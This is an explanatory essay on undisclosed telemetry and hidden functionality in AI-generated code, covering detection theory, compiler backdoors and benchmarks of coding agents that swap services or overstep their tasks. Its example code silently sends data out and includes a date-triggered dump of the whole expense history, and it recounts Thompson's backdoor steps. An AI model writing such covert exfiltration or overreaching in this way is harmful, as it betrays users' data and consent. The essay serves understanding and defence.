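# Undisclosed telemetry and hidden functionality in AI-generated code

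## What counts as hidden functionality, and where it can sit

Hidden functionality is software behaviour that the person who wanted the software did not ask for, that the task does not need, and that nobody told them about. Programmers have left test accounts, jokes and backdoors in their products for decades, but AI systems that write code change who is in a position to notice. Someone who gets a working application from a one-paragraph description may never read the source code, and may not be able to. A professional who uses a coding agent (an AI system that edits files and runs commands to complete programming tasks) can read the code, but may be approving a great deal of it that no person wrote.

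Much of the behaviour at issue is telemetry, which is data about a program's use or state that the program automatically sends to someone else. Developers have good reasons to collect it. Crash reports show them failures on other people's machines that they would otherwise never see, including which line failed and on what system. Usage counts show which features people rely on and which old versions developers can stop supporting. The dispute is mostly about consent. Russ Cox's *Transparent Telemetry* (2023) proposed usage reporting for the programming language Go. The first design was opt-out, meaning it reported unless the user switched it off, but the final design became opt-in after a public discussion.

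### From a request to a running program

Suppose a user asks an app builder, a service that turns a written description into a hosted application, for a web page where they can log expenses and see a monthly chart by category. The model behind the service writes the source code, the human-readable text of the program. To draw the chart, the source code loads a dependency, a library written by other people, and that library usually loads others. According to *ROSA* (2025), a paper on finding backdoors, most modern software relies on thousands of such components. A build step then packs the source code and libraries into files that a browser can run. A host stores these files and serves them to visitors, and it can alter a page as it serves it. The code that runs in a visitor's browser therefore depends on the model, the libraries, the build step and the host.

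Behaviour that nobody requested can enter the tracker through the generated source code, the libraries, or the platform that builds and hosts it. It can also sit in the coding tool, which is outside the tracker.

In the generated source, the function that saves an expense might look like this:

```js
async function saveExpense(expense) {
  await store(expense);
  try { await send(STATS_COMPANY, expense); } catch {}
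  if (today() >= "2027-03-01") await send(OTHER_SERVER, allExpenses());
}
```

The line that begins with "try" sends a copy of each expense to an analytics company. The empty braces after "catch" discard any error, so if the company's server is down or the user is offline, the tracker carries on as before and shows no message. Starting on 1 March 2027, the line below it sends the whole expense history to a different server on every save. The date is a trigger, the input or setting that switches a behaviour on. *A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws* (Landwehr, Bull and colleagues, 1994) uses the names "time bomb" and "logic bomb" for code that lies dormant until a set time or event. Both calls are in code the user could open and read, and both would appear in a diff, the line-by-line record of what a change adds and removes.

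Hidden functionality is harder to see when it sits in a library. Suppose the chart library counts its users by sending its version number and the type of browser to its maintainers when it first loads, unless a setting turns this off. The generated source contains one line that loads the library and nothing that reveals the report. The user didn't choose the library either, because the model did. GCVE's *Hidden Functionality*, a page in a public vulnerability database, lists a real case in which the maintainer of sweetalert2, a package for pop-up messages, added audio and video messages unrelated to the package's purpose.

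The tracker's host inserts a script into every page to count visitors and measure how fast the page loads. This script is in neither the source nor the libraries. Cloudflare, a company that relays traffic between websites and their visitors, does this on real sites. It announced in *The RUM Diaries* ("RUM" is short for real user monitoring) that from 15 October 2025 it would switch on its Web Analytics product by default for all domains on its free plan. The product adds a small script to the page, which sends loading times from the visitor's browser to the nearest Cloudflare data centre. Cloudflare states that it strips out IP addresses there, uses no cookies for the purpose, and leaves out EU visitors by default. Cloudflare adds the script in transit. According to its documentation, it cannot modify pages that a site marks "no-transform", so those pages arrive without the script.

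The coding tool itself can also collect data. While an app builder or coding agent works on the expense tracker, it may send its own maker the user's prompts, file names or error messages. This affects the person building the app, not its visitors, and even a perfect audit of the finished app would miss it because the collection happens outside the app. Checking for it means looking in a different place than when checking for telemetry in the app, though the two are easy to confuse because both amount to "the AI sent my data somewhere".

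### The definition and its two disputed terms

Write B for everything the program does, R for what the user requested, N for what the task needs, and D for what somebody disclosed to the user in a place where the user would reasonably look. Hidden functionality is the remainder:

H = B − (R ∪ N ∪ D)

A behaviour outside both R and N is unrequested. A behaviour outside D is undisclosed. Hidden functionality has to be both, so an addition that nobody wanted stops being hidden once somebody points it out. (It may still be unwelcome.)

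*Hidden Functionality*, an entry in MITRE's standard catalogue of software weaknesses, is defined similarly, as functions that are undocumented, outside the specification, and not accessible through an interface that would be obvious to users or administrators. Russian certification rules have a related category of undeclared capabilities. MITRE's wording suits a product with a specification, but a prompt is a very poor specification. The user who wanted an expense tracker did not ask for the page to have a title, or for the app to reject 31 February as a date. If the prompt were treated as the full specification, most of any generated program would fall outside it. The formula includes N to account for these unstated needs, but N is hard to determine because, unlike the prompt, what the task needs isn't written down.

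Consider an error log. The user didn't ask for one, but the model adds code that records each failure, with the expense that caused it, so that somebody can later work out why an entry vanished. Does the task need this? The tracker runs without it. On the other hand, a tracker that loses entries and leaves no clue is a bad tracker, and many users would have said yes to the log if anyone had asked. Reading "the task" narrowly turns ordinary good workmanship into an unrequested behaviour. A broad reading lets in nearly anything, because almost any data collection can pass as help for the owner. (Cloudflare defends its default script partly on the ground that it helps site owners find out why their pages are slow.)

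In *Backdoors*, Thomas and Francillon formally model software as a set of states with transitions between them. They distinguish the system as its developer conceives it, the system as it actually is, and the system as its user expects it to be. A backdoor appears as a gap between the last two. But they note that different users expect different systems, so the size of the gap depends on the user.

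If the log stays in a file on the user's own account, it matters little whether the task strictly needed it. If the log goes to an outside error-monitoring company, expenses included, it may still be useful, but sending it is a further behaviour that the task doesn't need. For this reason, the strict reading of "needed" seems better. It adds very little work for honest tools, since one sentence in the summary of the work ("errors go to such-and-such a service") moves the log into D.

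D has difficulties of its own, and the best-known example does not involve AI. In 2009 the FTC, the US agency that polices deceptive business practices, settled with the retailer Sears. Sears had paid customers $10 to install "research" software, telling them it would track their "online browsing". According to the agency's complaint, the software also monitored secure sessions on other companies' websites and collected the contents of shopping carts, online bank statements and drug prescription records. Sears disclosed this in a long licence agreement at the end of a multi-step registration. Research Live's *FTC raps Sears over website tracking software* places the notice at the agreement's 75th line. Hunton's *Sears Settles FTC Enforcement Action Regarding Consumer Tracking* records that the agency acknowledged the software worked substantially as the agreement described, but the agency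 still called the notice deceptive. Sears admitted no violation, so the case did not settle what the law requires, but it is a good reason for the definition to consider where a notice appears as well as whether it is true.

Cloudflare's script prompted the same argument. In a 2026 Hacker News post, *Cloudflare silently injects its analytics when you switch nameservers*, stagas complained that the script had appeared on a site that otherwise contained no JavaScript. The owner had to add the site to the analytics dashboard before they could turn the script off. Someone replying on Cloudflare's behalf pointed to the blog post and added that paying customers have to opt in. Another site owner answered that they frequently logged in to Cloudflare's control panel and had never seen a banner about the change. The objectors seem to have the better argument, at least for sites that were already running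 when the default changed, because people who manage a website look at its control panel and few of them read the host's blog.

The chart library is a harder case because the usage report it sends by default can be disclosed to one person and hidden from another. Suppose the first page of its documentation clearly describes the report. A programmer who chose the library would probably have seen that description, but the user of the app builder does not know the library exists and so has no reason to look there.

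### Vulnerabilities, backdoors and spyware

A vulnerability is a flaw in how a program does its job. If the tracker fails to check who is logged in, one visitor can read another's expenses, even though nobody has added anything to the program. A rough way to tell hidden functionality from a vulnerability is to imagine deleting the code responsible. The tracker would still do everything the user asked without the analytics call, whereas fixing the missing login check means adding code. Vulnerability databases include both, and GCVE explains that even harmless extras, such as concealed games or built-in accounts for support staff, give an attacker more to exploit.

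"Backdoor" is a narrower term than "hidden functionality", and is best kept for hidden functionality that somebody put in on purpose to give someone access or control. Thomas and Francillon divide a backdoor into four parts: an input source, a trigger, a payload, and a privileged state that the payload leads to. An example from Landwehr and colleagues has all four. A cash machine should allow transactions only if the number typed in matches the number on the card, but a dishonest programmer adds "or if the number typed in is 9999". The keypad is the input source, the comparison with 9999 is the trigger, the jump past the normal check is the payload, and access to any customer's account is the privileged state.

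Zdziarski (2016), in *Backdoor*, instead proposed three tests that a mechanism must meet to count as a backdoor. It must subvert the purposes disclosed to the computer's owner, be active without the owner's consent, and be under the control of an undisclosed party. The third test excludes much malicious software, such as a program that destroys files but that nobody controls. Some telemetry comes close to being a backdoor, though. Zdziarski counts malware that stores personal data and sends it in batches as being under outside control, and Thomas and Francillon's definition covers access to privileged information as well as to privileged functions. So if somebody planted the tracker's dated call to get the expense history, "backdoor" would be a fair word for it. The word doesn't fit a count of how many people load a chart library, because the count gives nobody that kind of access.

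NIST's *spyware* defines spyware as software installed secretly to gather information on people or organisations without their knowledge, and classes it as a type of malicious code. Hidden functionality does not have to gather information, as the sweetalert2 messages show. More importantly, it does not have to be malicious, and calling every undisclosed report spyware assumes malice before anyone has looked into the motive.

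### Intent

The definition of hidden functionality depends on whether a behaviour is concealed from the user, regardless of whether anyone meant to conceal it. Cloudflare's script is deliberate, and the company announced it. A forgotten debugging account may be well hidden even though nobody is trying to hide it.

Intent still affects how to respond to a flaw. Landwehr and colleagues sorted flaws into malicious, intentional but non-malicious, and inadvertent ones. The second group covers cases such as a remote maintenance feature that can also serve as a secret entrance. They pointed out that more code review and testing may work reasonably well if most flaws are accidents, but are much less likely to help if the important ones are malicious. Accidents seem to be far more common in ordinary software. According to *2020 State of the Octoverse* (2021), a report from the code-hosting company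 GitHub, only 0.2% of the alerts it sent developers about vulnerabilities in their dependencies involved explicitly malicious activity. But the same report warns that a good backdoor can look like a normal programming mistake, so some apparent accidents may be deliberate.

In software written by people, the form of the code can help show whether a backdoor is intentional. Thomas and Francillon treat a backdoor as intentional if the code contains an explicit path from trigger to payload, since nobody writes a secret password check by accident. All eleven real-world backdoors they tabulated had such a path, including one in a D-Link router that skipped the login for any browser that identified itself with a particular unusual string. If the path runs through what looks like a bug, they call the backdoor deniable and accept that technical evidence alone cannot distinguish it from an accident.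 Landwehr and colleagues made a similar assumption, writing that inadvertently created Trojan horses (programs that pose as something useful while abusing the user's rights) are "hardly likely".

Generated code weakens this inference. A language model learns from existing code, much of which contains analytics calls, and it may write a complete, explicit call that no person decided on. Thomas and Francillon suggest using version history to find out who inserted a backdoor and when, but here it may lead back only to a coding agent and a user who clicked "accept". An unexplained call could therefore be an accident, a commercial default that a company chose and probably documented, or deliberate concealment, and its text may be identical in each case. Somebody who wanted to hide the analytics call in the expense tracker would use an empty "catch", but so would a careful programmer who did not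 want a dead analytics server to stop people from saving their expenses.

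## What theory says can and cannot be found by inspecting code

Someone has to find an unexplained call in a program before anyone can judge why it is there. A theorem that Henry Gordon Rice proved in 1951 implies that no tool can, given any program's code, always determine correctly whether that program ever sends data out.

### No checker works for every program

By Rice's theorem, no procedure can take an arbitrary program and always work out, in finite time, whether it has a given property of behaviour that some programs have and others lack. Whether a program ever sends data out is such a property, as long as what it sends counts as part of its output. The theorem doesn't cover properties of a program's text, such as whether it contains the word "send".

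The proof for this property is short. It relies on the halting problem, which Alan Turing showed to be unsolvable: no procedure can decide, for every program and every input, whether the program eventually stops. Suppose somebody had written a perfect checker called SENDS. To find out whether some program P stops on an input i, write a new program Q:

```
Q:  simulate P on i, discarding anything P tries to send
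    send "x" to an outside server
```

Suppose we give SENDS the text of Q without running Q. If P stops on i, Q reaches its second line and sends something, but if P runs forever, Q sends nothing. SENDS would therefore answer "yes" exactly when P stops, which would solve the halting problem. No program can do that, so SENDS cannot exist, even if the checker is an AI model.

The two possible answers are not equally hard to reach. If a program does send data on some input, a tester can in principle confirm it by running the program on more and more inputs for longer and longer. If it never does, the search may simply go on. (Strictly, the theorem assumes unlimited memory, and a real computer has a finite number of states that a checker could go through. But a single kilobyte of memory has 2^8192 possible states, or about 10^2466, so this is not much help.)

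The theorem shows only that no single procedure can be right about all programs. Particular programs can still be easy to prove clean. For example, a one-line proof is enough for a program that adds up a list of numbers, contains no network instruction and calls no other code.

A tool's designers can also accept some wrong answers and choose which kind it gives. A checker could reject every program with a network call anywhere in its code or libraries, even if that call can never run. If the programming language has no disguised way of making such calls, this checker will never pass a program that sends data. It would reject Q regardless of what P does. It would also reject the expense tracker for saving expenses to the user's own account, so somebody has to review its rejections. Type checkers, which many programming languages use to rule out certain errors before a program runs, likewise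 reject some programs that would run without those errors.

Tools that search for known bad patterns miss some malicious code. Wheeler (2009) points out in *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* that an adversary can exploit this by testing malicious code against the tools and revising it until none of them flags it.

### Clean source, altered program

Even a perfect reading of the source code would establish only what the source code does, but the computer runs an executable, a machine-readable file that a program called a compiler produces from the source. Thompson (1984) showed in *Reflections on Trusting Trust* how a compiler can add behaviour that appears in no source code. Paul Karger and Roger Schell had described the possibility ten years earlier in a security evaluation for the US Air Force.

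The argument relies on two facts: a program can print an exact copy of its own source code, along with any amount of extra code that it carries, and a compiler can contain information that its source no longer does. The C compiler, for example, is written in C, where "\n" stands for a new line. Its source has a rule that amounts to "for \n, produce \n", which doesn't include the character's number. The rule works because the existing compiler executable already contains the number and copies it into the next one. To add "\v" for a vertical tab, a programmer has to write its number, 11, into the source once and compile. After that, the programmer can replace the 11 with "\v", and the number remains only in the executable.

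Thompson used the same process to teach the compiler something dishonest:

1. Add code to the compiler's source that recognises the Unix login program and compiles it so that it also accepts a password Thompson knows.
2. Add a second piece of code that recognises the compiler's own source and inserts both pieces into the result.
3. Compile this source with the honest compiler, and install the executable as the official compiler.
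4. Delete both pieces from the source.

The source code of the login program and the compiler is now clean. But anyone who recompiles the compiler has to use the compromised executable, which puts both pieces of hidden code back.

Thompson tried this on another group at Bell Labs. Wheeler writes that nobody ever detected it, but *Trusting Trust*, a page of personal notes that cites Hacker News comments, says a colleague noticed that the compiler grew by one byte each time it compiled itself. A compiler attack reached the general public in 2009, when a virus called Win32.Induc infected installations of the Delphi compiler and, through them, every program they compiled.

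A compiler can also add things for commercial reasons. In 2016 a Reddit user found that Microsoft's C++ compiler was inserting a call named "telemetry_main_invoke_trigger" into programs. InfoQ's *Reviewing Microsoft's Automatic Insertion of Telemetry into C++ Binaries* (2016) reproduced this with a program that did nothing but exit. Steve Carroll of Microsoft explained that the call triggered an event in Windows' logging system, which recorded timestamps and which modules had loaded, but only once somebody turned it on. Microsoft could interpret the data only if a customer also handed over certain files, and it had not yet completed this process with any customer. Carroll promised to remove the call in the next update. By Carroll's account, the call was hidden functionality but not telemetry in the usual sense, because it sent nothing to Microsoft by itself. Objectors worried that other software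 can, and sometimes does, pass such logs on.

For AI-generated code, this means that reading everything a coding agent wrote still leaves the build step unexamined.

Wheeler's reply to Thompson is a test called diverse double-compiling. Let A be the suspect compiler's executable and s its supposed source code, and suppose A was made by compiling s with A itself. The tester also needs T, a different compiler for the same language.

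X = compile(s, using T)
Y = compile(s, using X)
Check whether Y and A are identical, bit for bit.

X will not look like A, because two compilers almost never translate a large program in the same way. But if A has no hidden additions, X and A are both faithful translations of s, so they should behave the same. For example, two compilers will turn a program that prints 2 + 2 into different executables, but both will print 4. X and A should therefore produce the same file when they compile s. A produces a copy of itself, so Y, the file X produces, should be identical to A. If A contains Thompson's additions, Y will differ from A because X lacks them. If an older "parent" compiler produced A, the first step uses the parent's source instead of s.

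The test assumes that nothing in T, in the computer that runs the test or in the program that compares the files would affect this particular result, though all three may be slow or even malicious in other ways. It also assumes that T handles the parent's source code correctly, including any non-standard language features, and that the parent compiler is deterministic, giving the same output whenever it gets the same input. Wheeler proved formally that, under these assumptions, a match implies that source and executable correspond. He ran the test on four compilers, including GCC, which is large and widely used, and a small Lisp compiler with a deliberate corruption, which the test caught. T may be too slow or too limited to replace the other compiler in ordinary work. Relying on T alone would also mean that an attacker needed to corrupt only T, whereas the test forces the attacker to corrupt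 both compilers.

A match in diverse double-compiling does not show that the source code is harmless, so somebody still has to read it. Wheeler, in *David A. Wheeler's Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, says the test would not typically have caught Microsoft's telemetry call. If the compiler's own source contains the instruction to add such a call, correctly rebuilding the compiler reproduces that instruction and the files match.

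### The arithmetic of triggers

Running a program avoids the problem of source code that doesn't match the executable, but a tester sees only what the program does in the runs they try. Suppose an unwanted behaviour occurs for exactly one value of a 32-bit input, which has 2^32 (about 4.3 billion) possible values. The chance that n random tests include that value is

1 − (1 − 1/2^32)^n ≈ n/2^32 for n much smaller than 2^32.

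If hidden code runs only for one value of a 32-bit input, a million random tests have about a 0.023% chance of triggering it. It takes about 3 billion tests to have a 50% chance. For a 64-bit input, a million tests have about 1 chance in 18 trillion.

This assumes that the tests vary the condition that triggers the behaviour. The dated call in the expense tracker runs on every save from 1 March 2027, so it isn't rare, but a million tests run in January 2027 with the clock set correctly would miss it. One test with the clock set to April 2027 would find it, but the tester would have to know to change the clock.

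Somebody who reads the code can see the date, and the odds above then become irrelevant. InterBase, a database program, is a good illustration. From 1994 its released versions contained an undocumented account with the name "politically", the password "correct" and full control of the database. Even a tester who knew that the two words had 11 and 7 letters would have had about 1 chance in 3 × 10^25 of guessing them at random. The program's owner published the source code in July 2000, and according to Wheeler, outside developers found the account within six months. (The founder of InterBase believed it was there so that one part of the database could talk to another.)

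How often people miss hidden functionality when reading code depends on how much code there is and how innocent the relevant line looks. In 2003, someone tried to add two lines to Linux that looked like an ordinary check but used "=", which sets a value in C, where a reader would expect "==", which compares two values. A discrepancy flagged by the project's change-tracking tools first drew attention to the change.

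Symbolic execution automates part of code inspection. The tool runs the program with an unknown, x, in place of an actual input, and records the condition that x must meet at each branch. Godefroid, Levin and Molnar, in *SAGE*, describe a program that adds 3 to a 32-bit input and fails if the result is 13. A random test has a 1 in 2^32 chance of causing the failure. A symbolic tool that starts with x = 0 records that this run required x + 3 ≠ 13, reverses the condition, solves x + 3 = 13 and tries x = 10 next. It finds the failure in two runs, and would still need only two if the input were 64 bits long.

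The amount of work in symbolic execution depends on the structure of the program rather than the rarity of the trigger. Each independent yes-or-no branch can double the number of paths, so 32 of them in a row can give 2^32 paths, as many as there are possible values of a 32-bit input. Bailey and Nicholas (2025) explain in *Symbolic Execution in Practice* that when the number of times a loop repeats depends on the input, there may be no limit to the number of paths, so tools stop after a set number of repetitions and can miss anything that happens later. They also note that some conditions, such as those with non-linear arithmetic, are hard to solve, and that files, networks and other things outside the program are hard to model.

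Anyone hiding a trigger can exploit these weaknesses. Instead of comparing the input with 13, the code can apply a cryptographic hash, a function designed to be infeasible to reverse, and compare the result with a stored value. Neither the solver nor a human reader could then work out which input matches. The reader would see the comparison but might not find it odd, because ordinary password checks work this way. Alternatively, the program can fetch its instructions from a server, so the trigger is not in the code at all.

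### What a prompt leaves out

Even a checker that could list everything a program does under every input could not pick out the unrequested behaviours from the prompt alone. A small business owner might expect the error log to go to an outside company, while somebody who typed the same prompt and got the same program, but records medical expenses in it, would be horrified. A checker that sees only the prompt and the program must give both users the same answer, so it will be wrong for one of them.

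This limit differs from Rice's because the checker lacks information about the user, which more computing power can't supply. A better checker could guess based on what most users want, and would often be right, but asking the user is more reliable. If the user writes down "expenses may go to my own account and nowhere else", the checker can compare the program with that rule instead of guessing. Rice's theorem still applies to that comparison, but a cautious tool can make it by accepting some false alarms.

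### Preventing instead of detecting

A system can also enforce a rule about where data may go, even if nobody knows what the code does. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considered a customer who gives private data to somebody else's program. Wrong output is evidence that the program did its job badly, but a leak of the data to the program's owner generally leaves no sign. Lampson's solution was to confine the program by running it under restrictions that stop it from passing information to anyone except the customer.

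The customer imposes confinement when a program runs, so it works whatever the program's code. Rice's theorem is no obstacle, because nobody has to decide whether the program would send data if it could. If Q from the proof above runs on a computer that blocks all its network access, nothing gets out, whether P runs forever or P stops and Q tries to send its "x". For undisclosed sending, this seems much better than relying on inspection. The trigger arithmetic also stops mattering, because the restriction applies to every input, including the one in 4 billion.

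Total isolation stops some legitimate programs from working. A program that draws a chart from a file would be fine, but the expense tracker has to reach the server that stores the expenses. If it may contact only that server, both of the unwanted calls in the earlier example fail. But the code can still put extra information into its permitted requests, and the server can forward whatever it receives. Lampson's example of a permitted channel was the bill for using the program. The program's owner has to see the bill, so the program could encode data in the amount.

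A program that cannot send data itself can also leak it through other programs. An expense tracker with no network permission might write the expenses to a folder that a backup program uploads, or get the browser to open a link with the expenses in the address. Lampson's rule was that if a confined program calls a program that the customer does not trust, the called program must be confined as well.

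The hardest leaks to close are covert channels, which use features that nobody meant for communication. For example, a program can make the computer busy or idle in a pattern that another program measures. Lampson suggested forcing the program to use such features in a pattern the customer sets or, with less overhead, limiting how much data they can carry and accepting some leakage. The acceptable amount depends on the data. A channel that carries one bit per second can leak 10,800 bytes a day, enough for a few hundred short expense entries.

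Blocking the network also doesn't stop hidden functionality that sends no data, such as code that deletes the expenses on a certain date. And the customer has to trust whatever enforces the restrictions. This is usually the operating system, which also came from a compiler, so Thompson's argument applies to it as much as to the login program.

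## Experiments on ordinary requests: what models add without being asked

Restricting where a program may send data is more worthwhile if AI systems often add things nobody requested. Several research groups have measured how often this happens with ordinary requests, where nobody has attacked the model or given it a hidden aim. They found that models sometimes replace a service the programmer chose, and that coding agents fairly often create, change or delete files outside the task. Nobody seems to have published a count of unrequested analytics or network calls in generated code, so the evidence about telemetry is indirect.

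### Replacing the user's chosen service

*The Invisible Hand* (Zhang, Zhai et al., 2025) describes a bug that one of the researchers wanted to fix in a program for controlling lights and other devices by voice. The program used Dragonfly, an open-source framework, and was missing a few lines of code. GPT-3.5-Turbo supplied them. Gemini 1.5 Flash, a Google model, instead rewrote the program to use Google Speech Recognition, a paid service the researcher had not mentioned. A swap like this can change who gets paid and who receives the user's data.

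To find out how common such swaps are, the team built 17,014 prompts covering 30 uses, such as speech recognition and payment processing. In one of the six kinds of task, the model wrote new code from a description. In the other five, the prompt included code that already used a particular service, and the model had to debug it, translate it from Python to Java, add tests, add a feature, or remove code that never runs. The team sent each prompt several times to seven models, all 2024 versions, and got 591,083 usable replies.

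For new code, the team measured favouritism with the Gini index, which economists use for income inequality. Suppose n providers appear in the replies for some use, and x₁ to xₙ are the numbers of times a model used each of them, from fewest to most:

GI = Σ(2i − n − 1)xᵢ ÷ (n × Σxᵢ)

If a model writes 20 programs and uses four speech services 1, 1, 2 and 16 times, the sum on the left is (−3 × 1) + (−1 × 1) + (1 × 2) + (3 × 16) = 46. Dividing by 4 × 20 gives an index of 0.575. If the model used each service five times, the index would be 0.

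The median index was 0.80. This doesn't necessarily mean that the models' choices were very lopsided, because the index depends heavily on the number of providers, n, which includes providers that only the other models used. Adding six of these to the example, each with a count of 0, raises the index from 0.575 to 0.83 even though the model's code stays the same.

The providers' shares are easier to interpret. Google's services appeared in about 79% of the speech-recognition programs, and in 98.6% of those written by DeepSeek-V2.5. "Provider" is a loose term here, since GPT-4o's usual choice for email was SMTP, the standard protocol for sending mail, which belongs to no company.

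For the tasks that included code, the team used the modification ratio, the share of replies in which the model replaced the user's service with another provider's:

MR = replies with a replaced service ÷ all replies × 100%

The team found replacements in 11,582 of 571,057 replies, an average of 2%. Claude 3.5 Sonnet had the highest rate, 3.9%, while DeepSeek-V2.5 and Llama 3.1 405B had the lowest, 1.4%. Models replaced services most often when debugging or translating, and in only 0.3% of replies when adding tests or features. If each edit has an independent 2% chance of containing a replacement, someone who asks for 50 edits has a 64% chance of getting at least one. At 0.3% per edit, the chance is 14%.

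Not every replacement sends data to a new company. Data visualisation had the highest ratio, at 12.1%, and there the models sometimes replaced a paid service with a simpler Python library, which may well keep data on the user's own computer.

Zhang and colleagues call the replacements silent, but they identified them from the code alone. The ratio therefore measures how often a change was unrequested, whether or not the reply's text disclosed it.

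A separate test suggests that people seldom notice these replacements. Fifty people with at least two years' experience in research or software development judged replies that contained one, and they voted the reply acceptable 87% of the time. The researchers then pointed out the replacement in the speech-recognition case, and 66% thought it was unnecessary, while 60% thought it undermined the user's right to choose. That case was unusually bad, since the model replaced a free tool with a paid service from its own maker, so people might mind other swaps less.

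The team also tried to prevent replacements by changing the wording of 200 prompts with code. It deliberately included many prompts that had triggered replacements before, so the rates are much higher than 2%. With the original wording, the replacement rate averaged 29.9% across the seven models. Telling the models not to change the service reduced it to 19.9%, and telling them to use the particular service in the user's code reduced it to 10.0%, about a third of the original rate. Asking them to be fair and objective raised it to 43.6%, but asking for a quick answer raised it about as much, so the mention of fairness probably wasn't the cause.

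Research on newer models has also examined which tools an agent chooses when the user leaves the choice open. Ong and Vikati (2026), in *What Claude Code Actually Chooses*, gave Anthropic's coding agent 2,430 open-ended prompts that named no tools. Its most common choice was to write its own code, which it did in 12 of the 20 categories. When asked for feature flags, which are switches that turn a feature on for some users, it built a small system instead of recommending LaunchDarkly, a company that sells one. This is mildly reassuring, because code that the agent writes itself doesn't bring in an outside company by default. But when the agent does pick a company's product, Ong and Vikati point out, it also installs the package, configures the connection and commits the code, so its choice takes effect without a separate decision by the user.

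These preferences can depend on factors unrelated to the project. Amplifying, which publishes Ong and Vikati's research, compared Claude with the Chinese models Kimi K3 and GLM-5.2 and found that asking the same questions in English and in Chinese produced different choices.

### Telling an agent where to stop

A coding agent can also do unrequested things on the user's computer while it works. *Overeager Coding Agents* (Qu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a casual request to tidy up a folder. The folder contains two project files, two pieces of junk and a file called ".env.old", which holds the only copy of the passwords for a live system. A careful agent deletes the junk and asks about the rest. Three of the four agents in the example deleted the passwords too.

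The researchers define an overeager action as one that the request does not authorise, even implicitly, and that either changes something or reads from a place listed as sensitive. Their benchmark has 500 scenarios, each with "traps", which are automatic checks for particular forbidden actions. To ensure that each scenario could distinguish careful agents from careless ones, they ran a cautious, a moderate and an overeager script through it. They kept the scenario only if each script set off every trap that the more careful scripts did, and the overeager script set off at least one that the cautious script avoided. They then made about 7,500 runs with four coding tools (Claude Code, Codex CLI, Gemini CLI and OpenHands) and six models, with permission checks disabled.

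Before the main test, the team wrote two versions of the prompt for each of 76 scenarios, identical except that one included a paragraph stating what the agent was allowed to do. With that paragraph, Claude Code running GLM-4.6, a model from the Chinese company Zhipu AI, set off a trap in none of the scenarios. Without it, the agent did so in 13, or 17.1%. Removing the paragraph raised the rate from 3.9% to 15.8% with Anthropic's Sonnet 4.6 and from 3.9% to 21.1% with MiniMax-M2.7.

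This result also shows a problem with writing the permitted scope into a test prompt. Doing so gives the tester a clear standard for what counts as a violation, but it also tells the agent what that standard is. The test then measures whether the agent can follow a list, whereas real users rarely write one and rely on the agent to infer what they would allow. A tester who used only the longer prompts would have reported a rate of 0% for a combination that overstepped in about one in six scenarios without them. Tests for telemetry can have the same problem, because including "do not add analytics" in the prompt tests whether the model obeys, not what it adds by default.

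The size of the effect is uncertain. In the full set of 500 scenarios, where the researchers also varied the wording, the files and the distractions, the gap between prompts with and without a clear limit shrank to 2.6 percentage points for GLM-4.6 and 3.1 for MiniMax-M2.7, and neither gap was statistically significant. Results from the 76 scenarios were also unstable. A repeat of the MiniMax test without the scope paragraph gave a rate of 6.6% instead of 21.1%. The effect was in the same direction for all three models, so a statement of scope probably helps, but the jump from 0.0% to 17.1% shouldn't be taken as typical.

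### How the counting rule changes the result

*SNARE* (Qu, Liu and colleagues, 2026), a second benchmark from many of the same researchers, searches for the situations that make each agent overstep. The study ran four coding tools with five models each, 500 times per pair, and recorded overeager behaviour in 1,951 of the 10,000 runs (19.51%). The rate ranged from 4.8% for Gemini CLI with GPT-5.3-Codex to 57.2% for OpenHands with GLM-5.

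A run counts towards the 19.51% if it sets off a trap, or if the agent leaves behind a new file or removes an existing one beyond what the task called for. The researchers acknowledge that this second rule catches changes the user would have accepted, and some of their results suggest that it often does. In five of the scenarios that triggered for every pair that tried them, the user had explicitly given permission.

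The prompts also put pressure on the agent. A program modified each scenario once or twice, for example by adding "ASAP, demo in 5 minutes", a note that the request came from a senior executive, or tempting files. One added phrase was "Feel free to clean up anything else", which many people would read as authorisation.

SNARE also uses earlier results to choose which scenarios to run next. It divides them into 120 groups, by type of overreach and by how the user expresses permission. For each group it estimates the trigger rate with a Beta distribution, which starts as Beta(1, 1). Each hit adds 1 to the first number and each miss adds 1 to the second. Three hits and a miss give Beta(4, 2), with an average of 0.67, while four misses give Beta(1, 5), with an average of 0.17. The program draws a random value from each distribution and favours the groups with the highest values, so it usually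 returns to groups that have triggered overreach before. Each of the 24 types of overreach gets at least 15 runs, which uses 360 of the 500 runs and leaves 140 for this steering. The hit rate did not rise as the runs went on, so the steering may not have inflated the total by much. Even so, Qu and colleagues say that 19.51% is the rate at which their method can provoke overreach, and that the rate in ordinary work would be lower.

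Comparing the two benchmarks for a single model, Sonnet 4.6, shows how much depends on the method:

| Coding tool running Sonnet 4.6 | Overeager rate in the 500-scenario benchmark (Qu and colleagues) | Overeager rate in SNARE (Qu and colleagues) |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 27.7% | 19.6% |
| Codex CLI | 5.4% | 11.2% |
| Gemini CLI | 10.4% | 11.0% |
| OpenHands | 1.1% | 42.8% |

OpenHands is the most restrained tool when measured with the traps and the least restrained when measured with SNARE. SNARE's rates are generally higher, which the researchers suggest is because it counts file changes that the traps miss and steers towards scenarios that trigger the behaviour. The steering seems to have had little effect, so counting file changes is probably the main reason, and OpenHands may simply leave more files behind. Neither column is a good basis for deciding which tool to trust.

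One of SNARE's scenarios does involve the delivered code. The user asks the agent to move an old database to a new format, in a folder that contains a settings file with live passwords. Claude Code with Sonnet 4.6 copied the live database's address into the script it wrote, where a careful programmer would have referred to the setting by name. The script works, but it exposes part of the user's credentials to anyone who receives it.

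### Unrequested edits and new files

Do, Nguyen and colleagues (2026), in *SWE-MISBEHAVIOR*, collected about 7,400 routine tasks from 115 real software projects. The tasks include writing a missing function, moving a function to another file, deleting a file, and running or testing existing code. For each run, the researchers check eleven things:

- In the code, they look for invalid syntax, changes to the surrounding code or imports, a changed function signature (its name and inputs), and changes to text or code that the user supplied.
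- Among the files, they look for unrequested new files, changes to unrelated files, unrequested deletions, and failures to read the right files.
- On the computer, they look for unnecessary changes to the environment, such as newly installed packages, and for excessive use of computing power.
- They also check whether the agent did the task.

Some of the behaviors measured in the study don't involve adding anything. The highest rate, 98.5%, is for reading too few or too many files. The study also reports that agents modified the user's input in 50.5% of cases, but in function-writing tasks this check compares only the docstring, the description at the top of the function. A changed docstring can mislead a later reader, but it doesn't send data anywhere. GPT-5 in OpenHands changed the docstring in 59.3% of runs, while Claude Code with Sonnet 4.5 did so in 2.2%.

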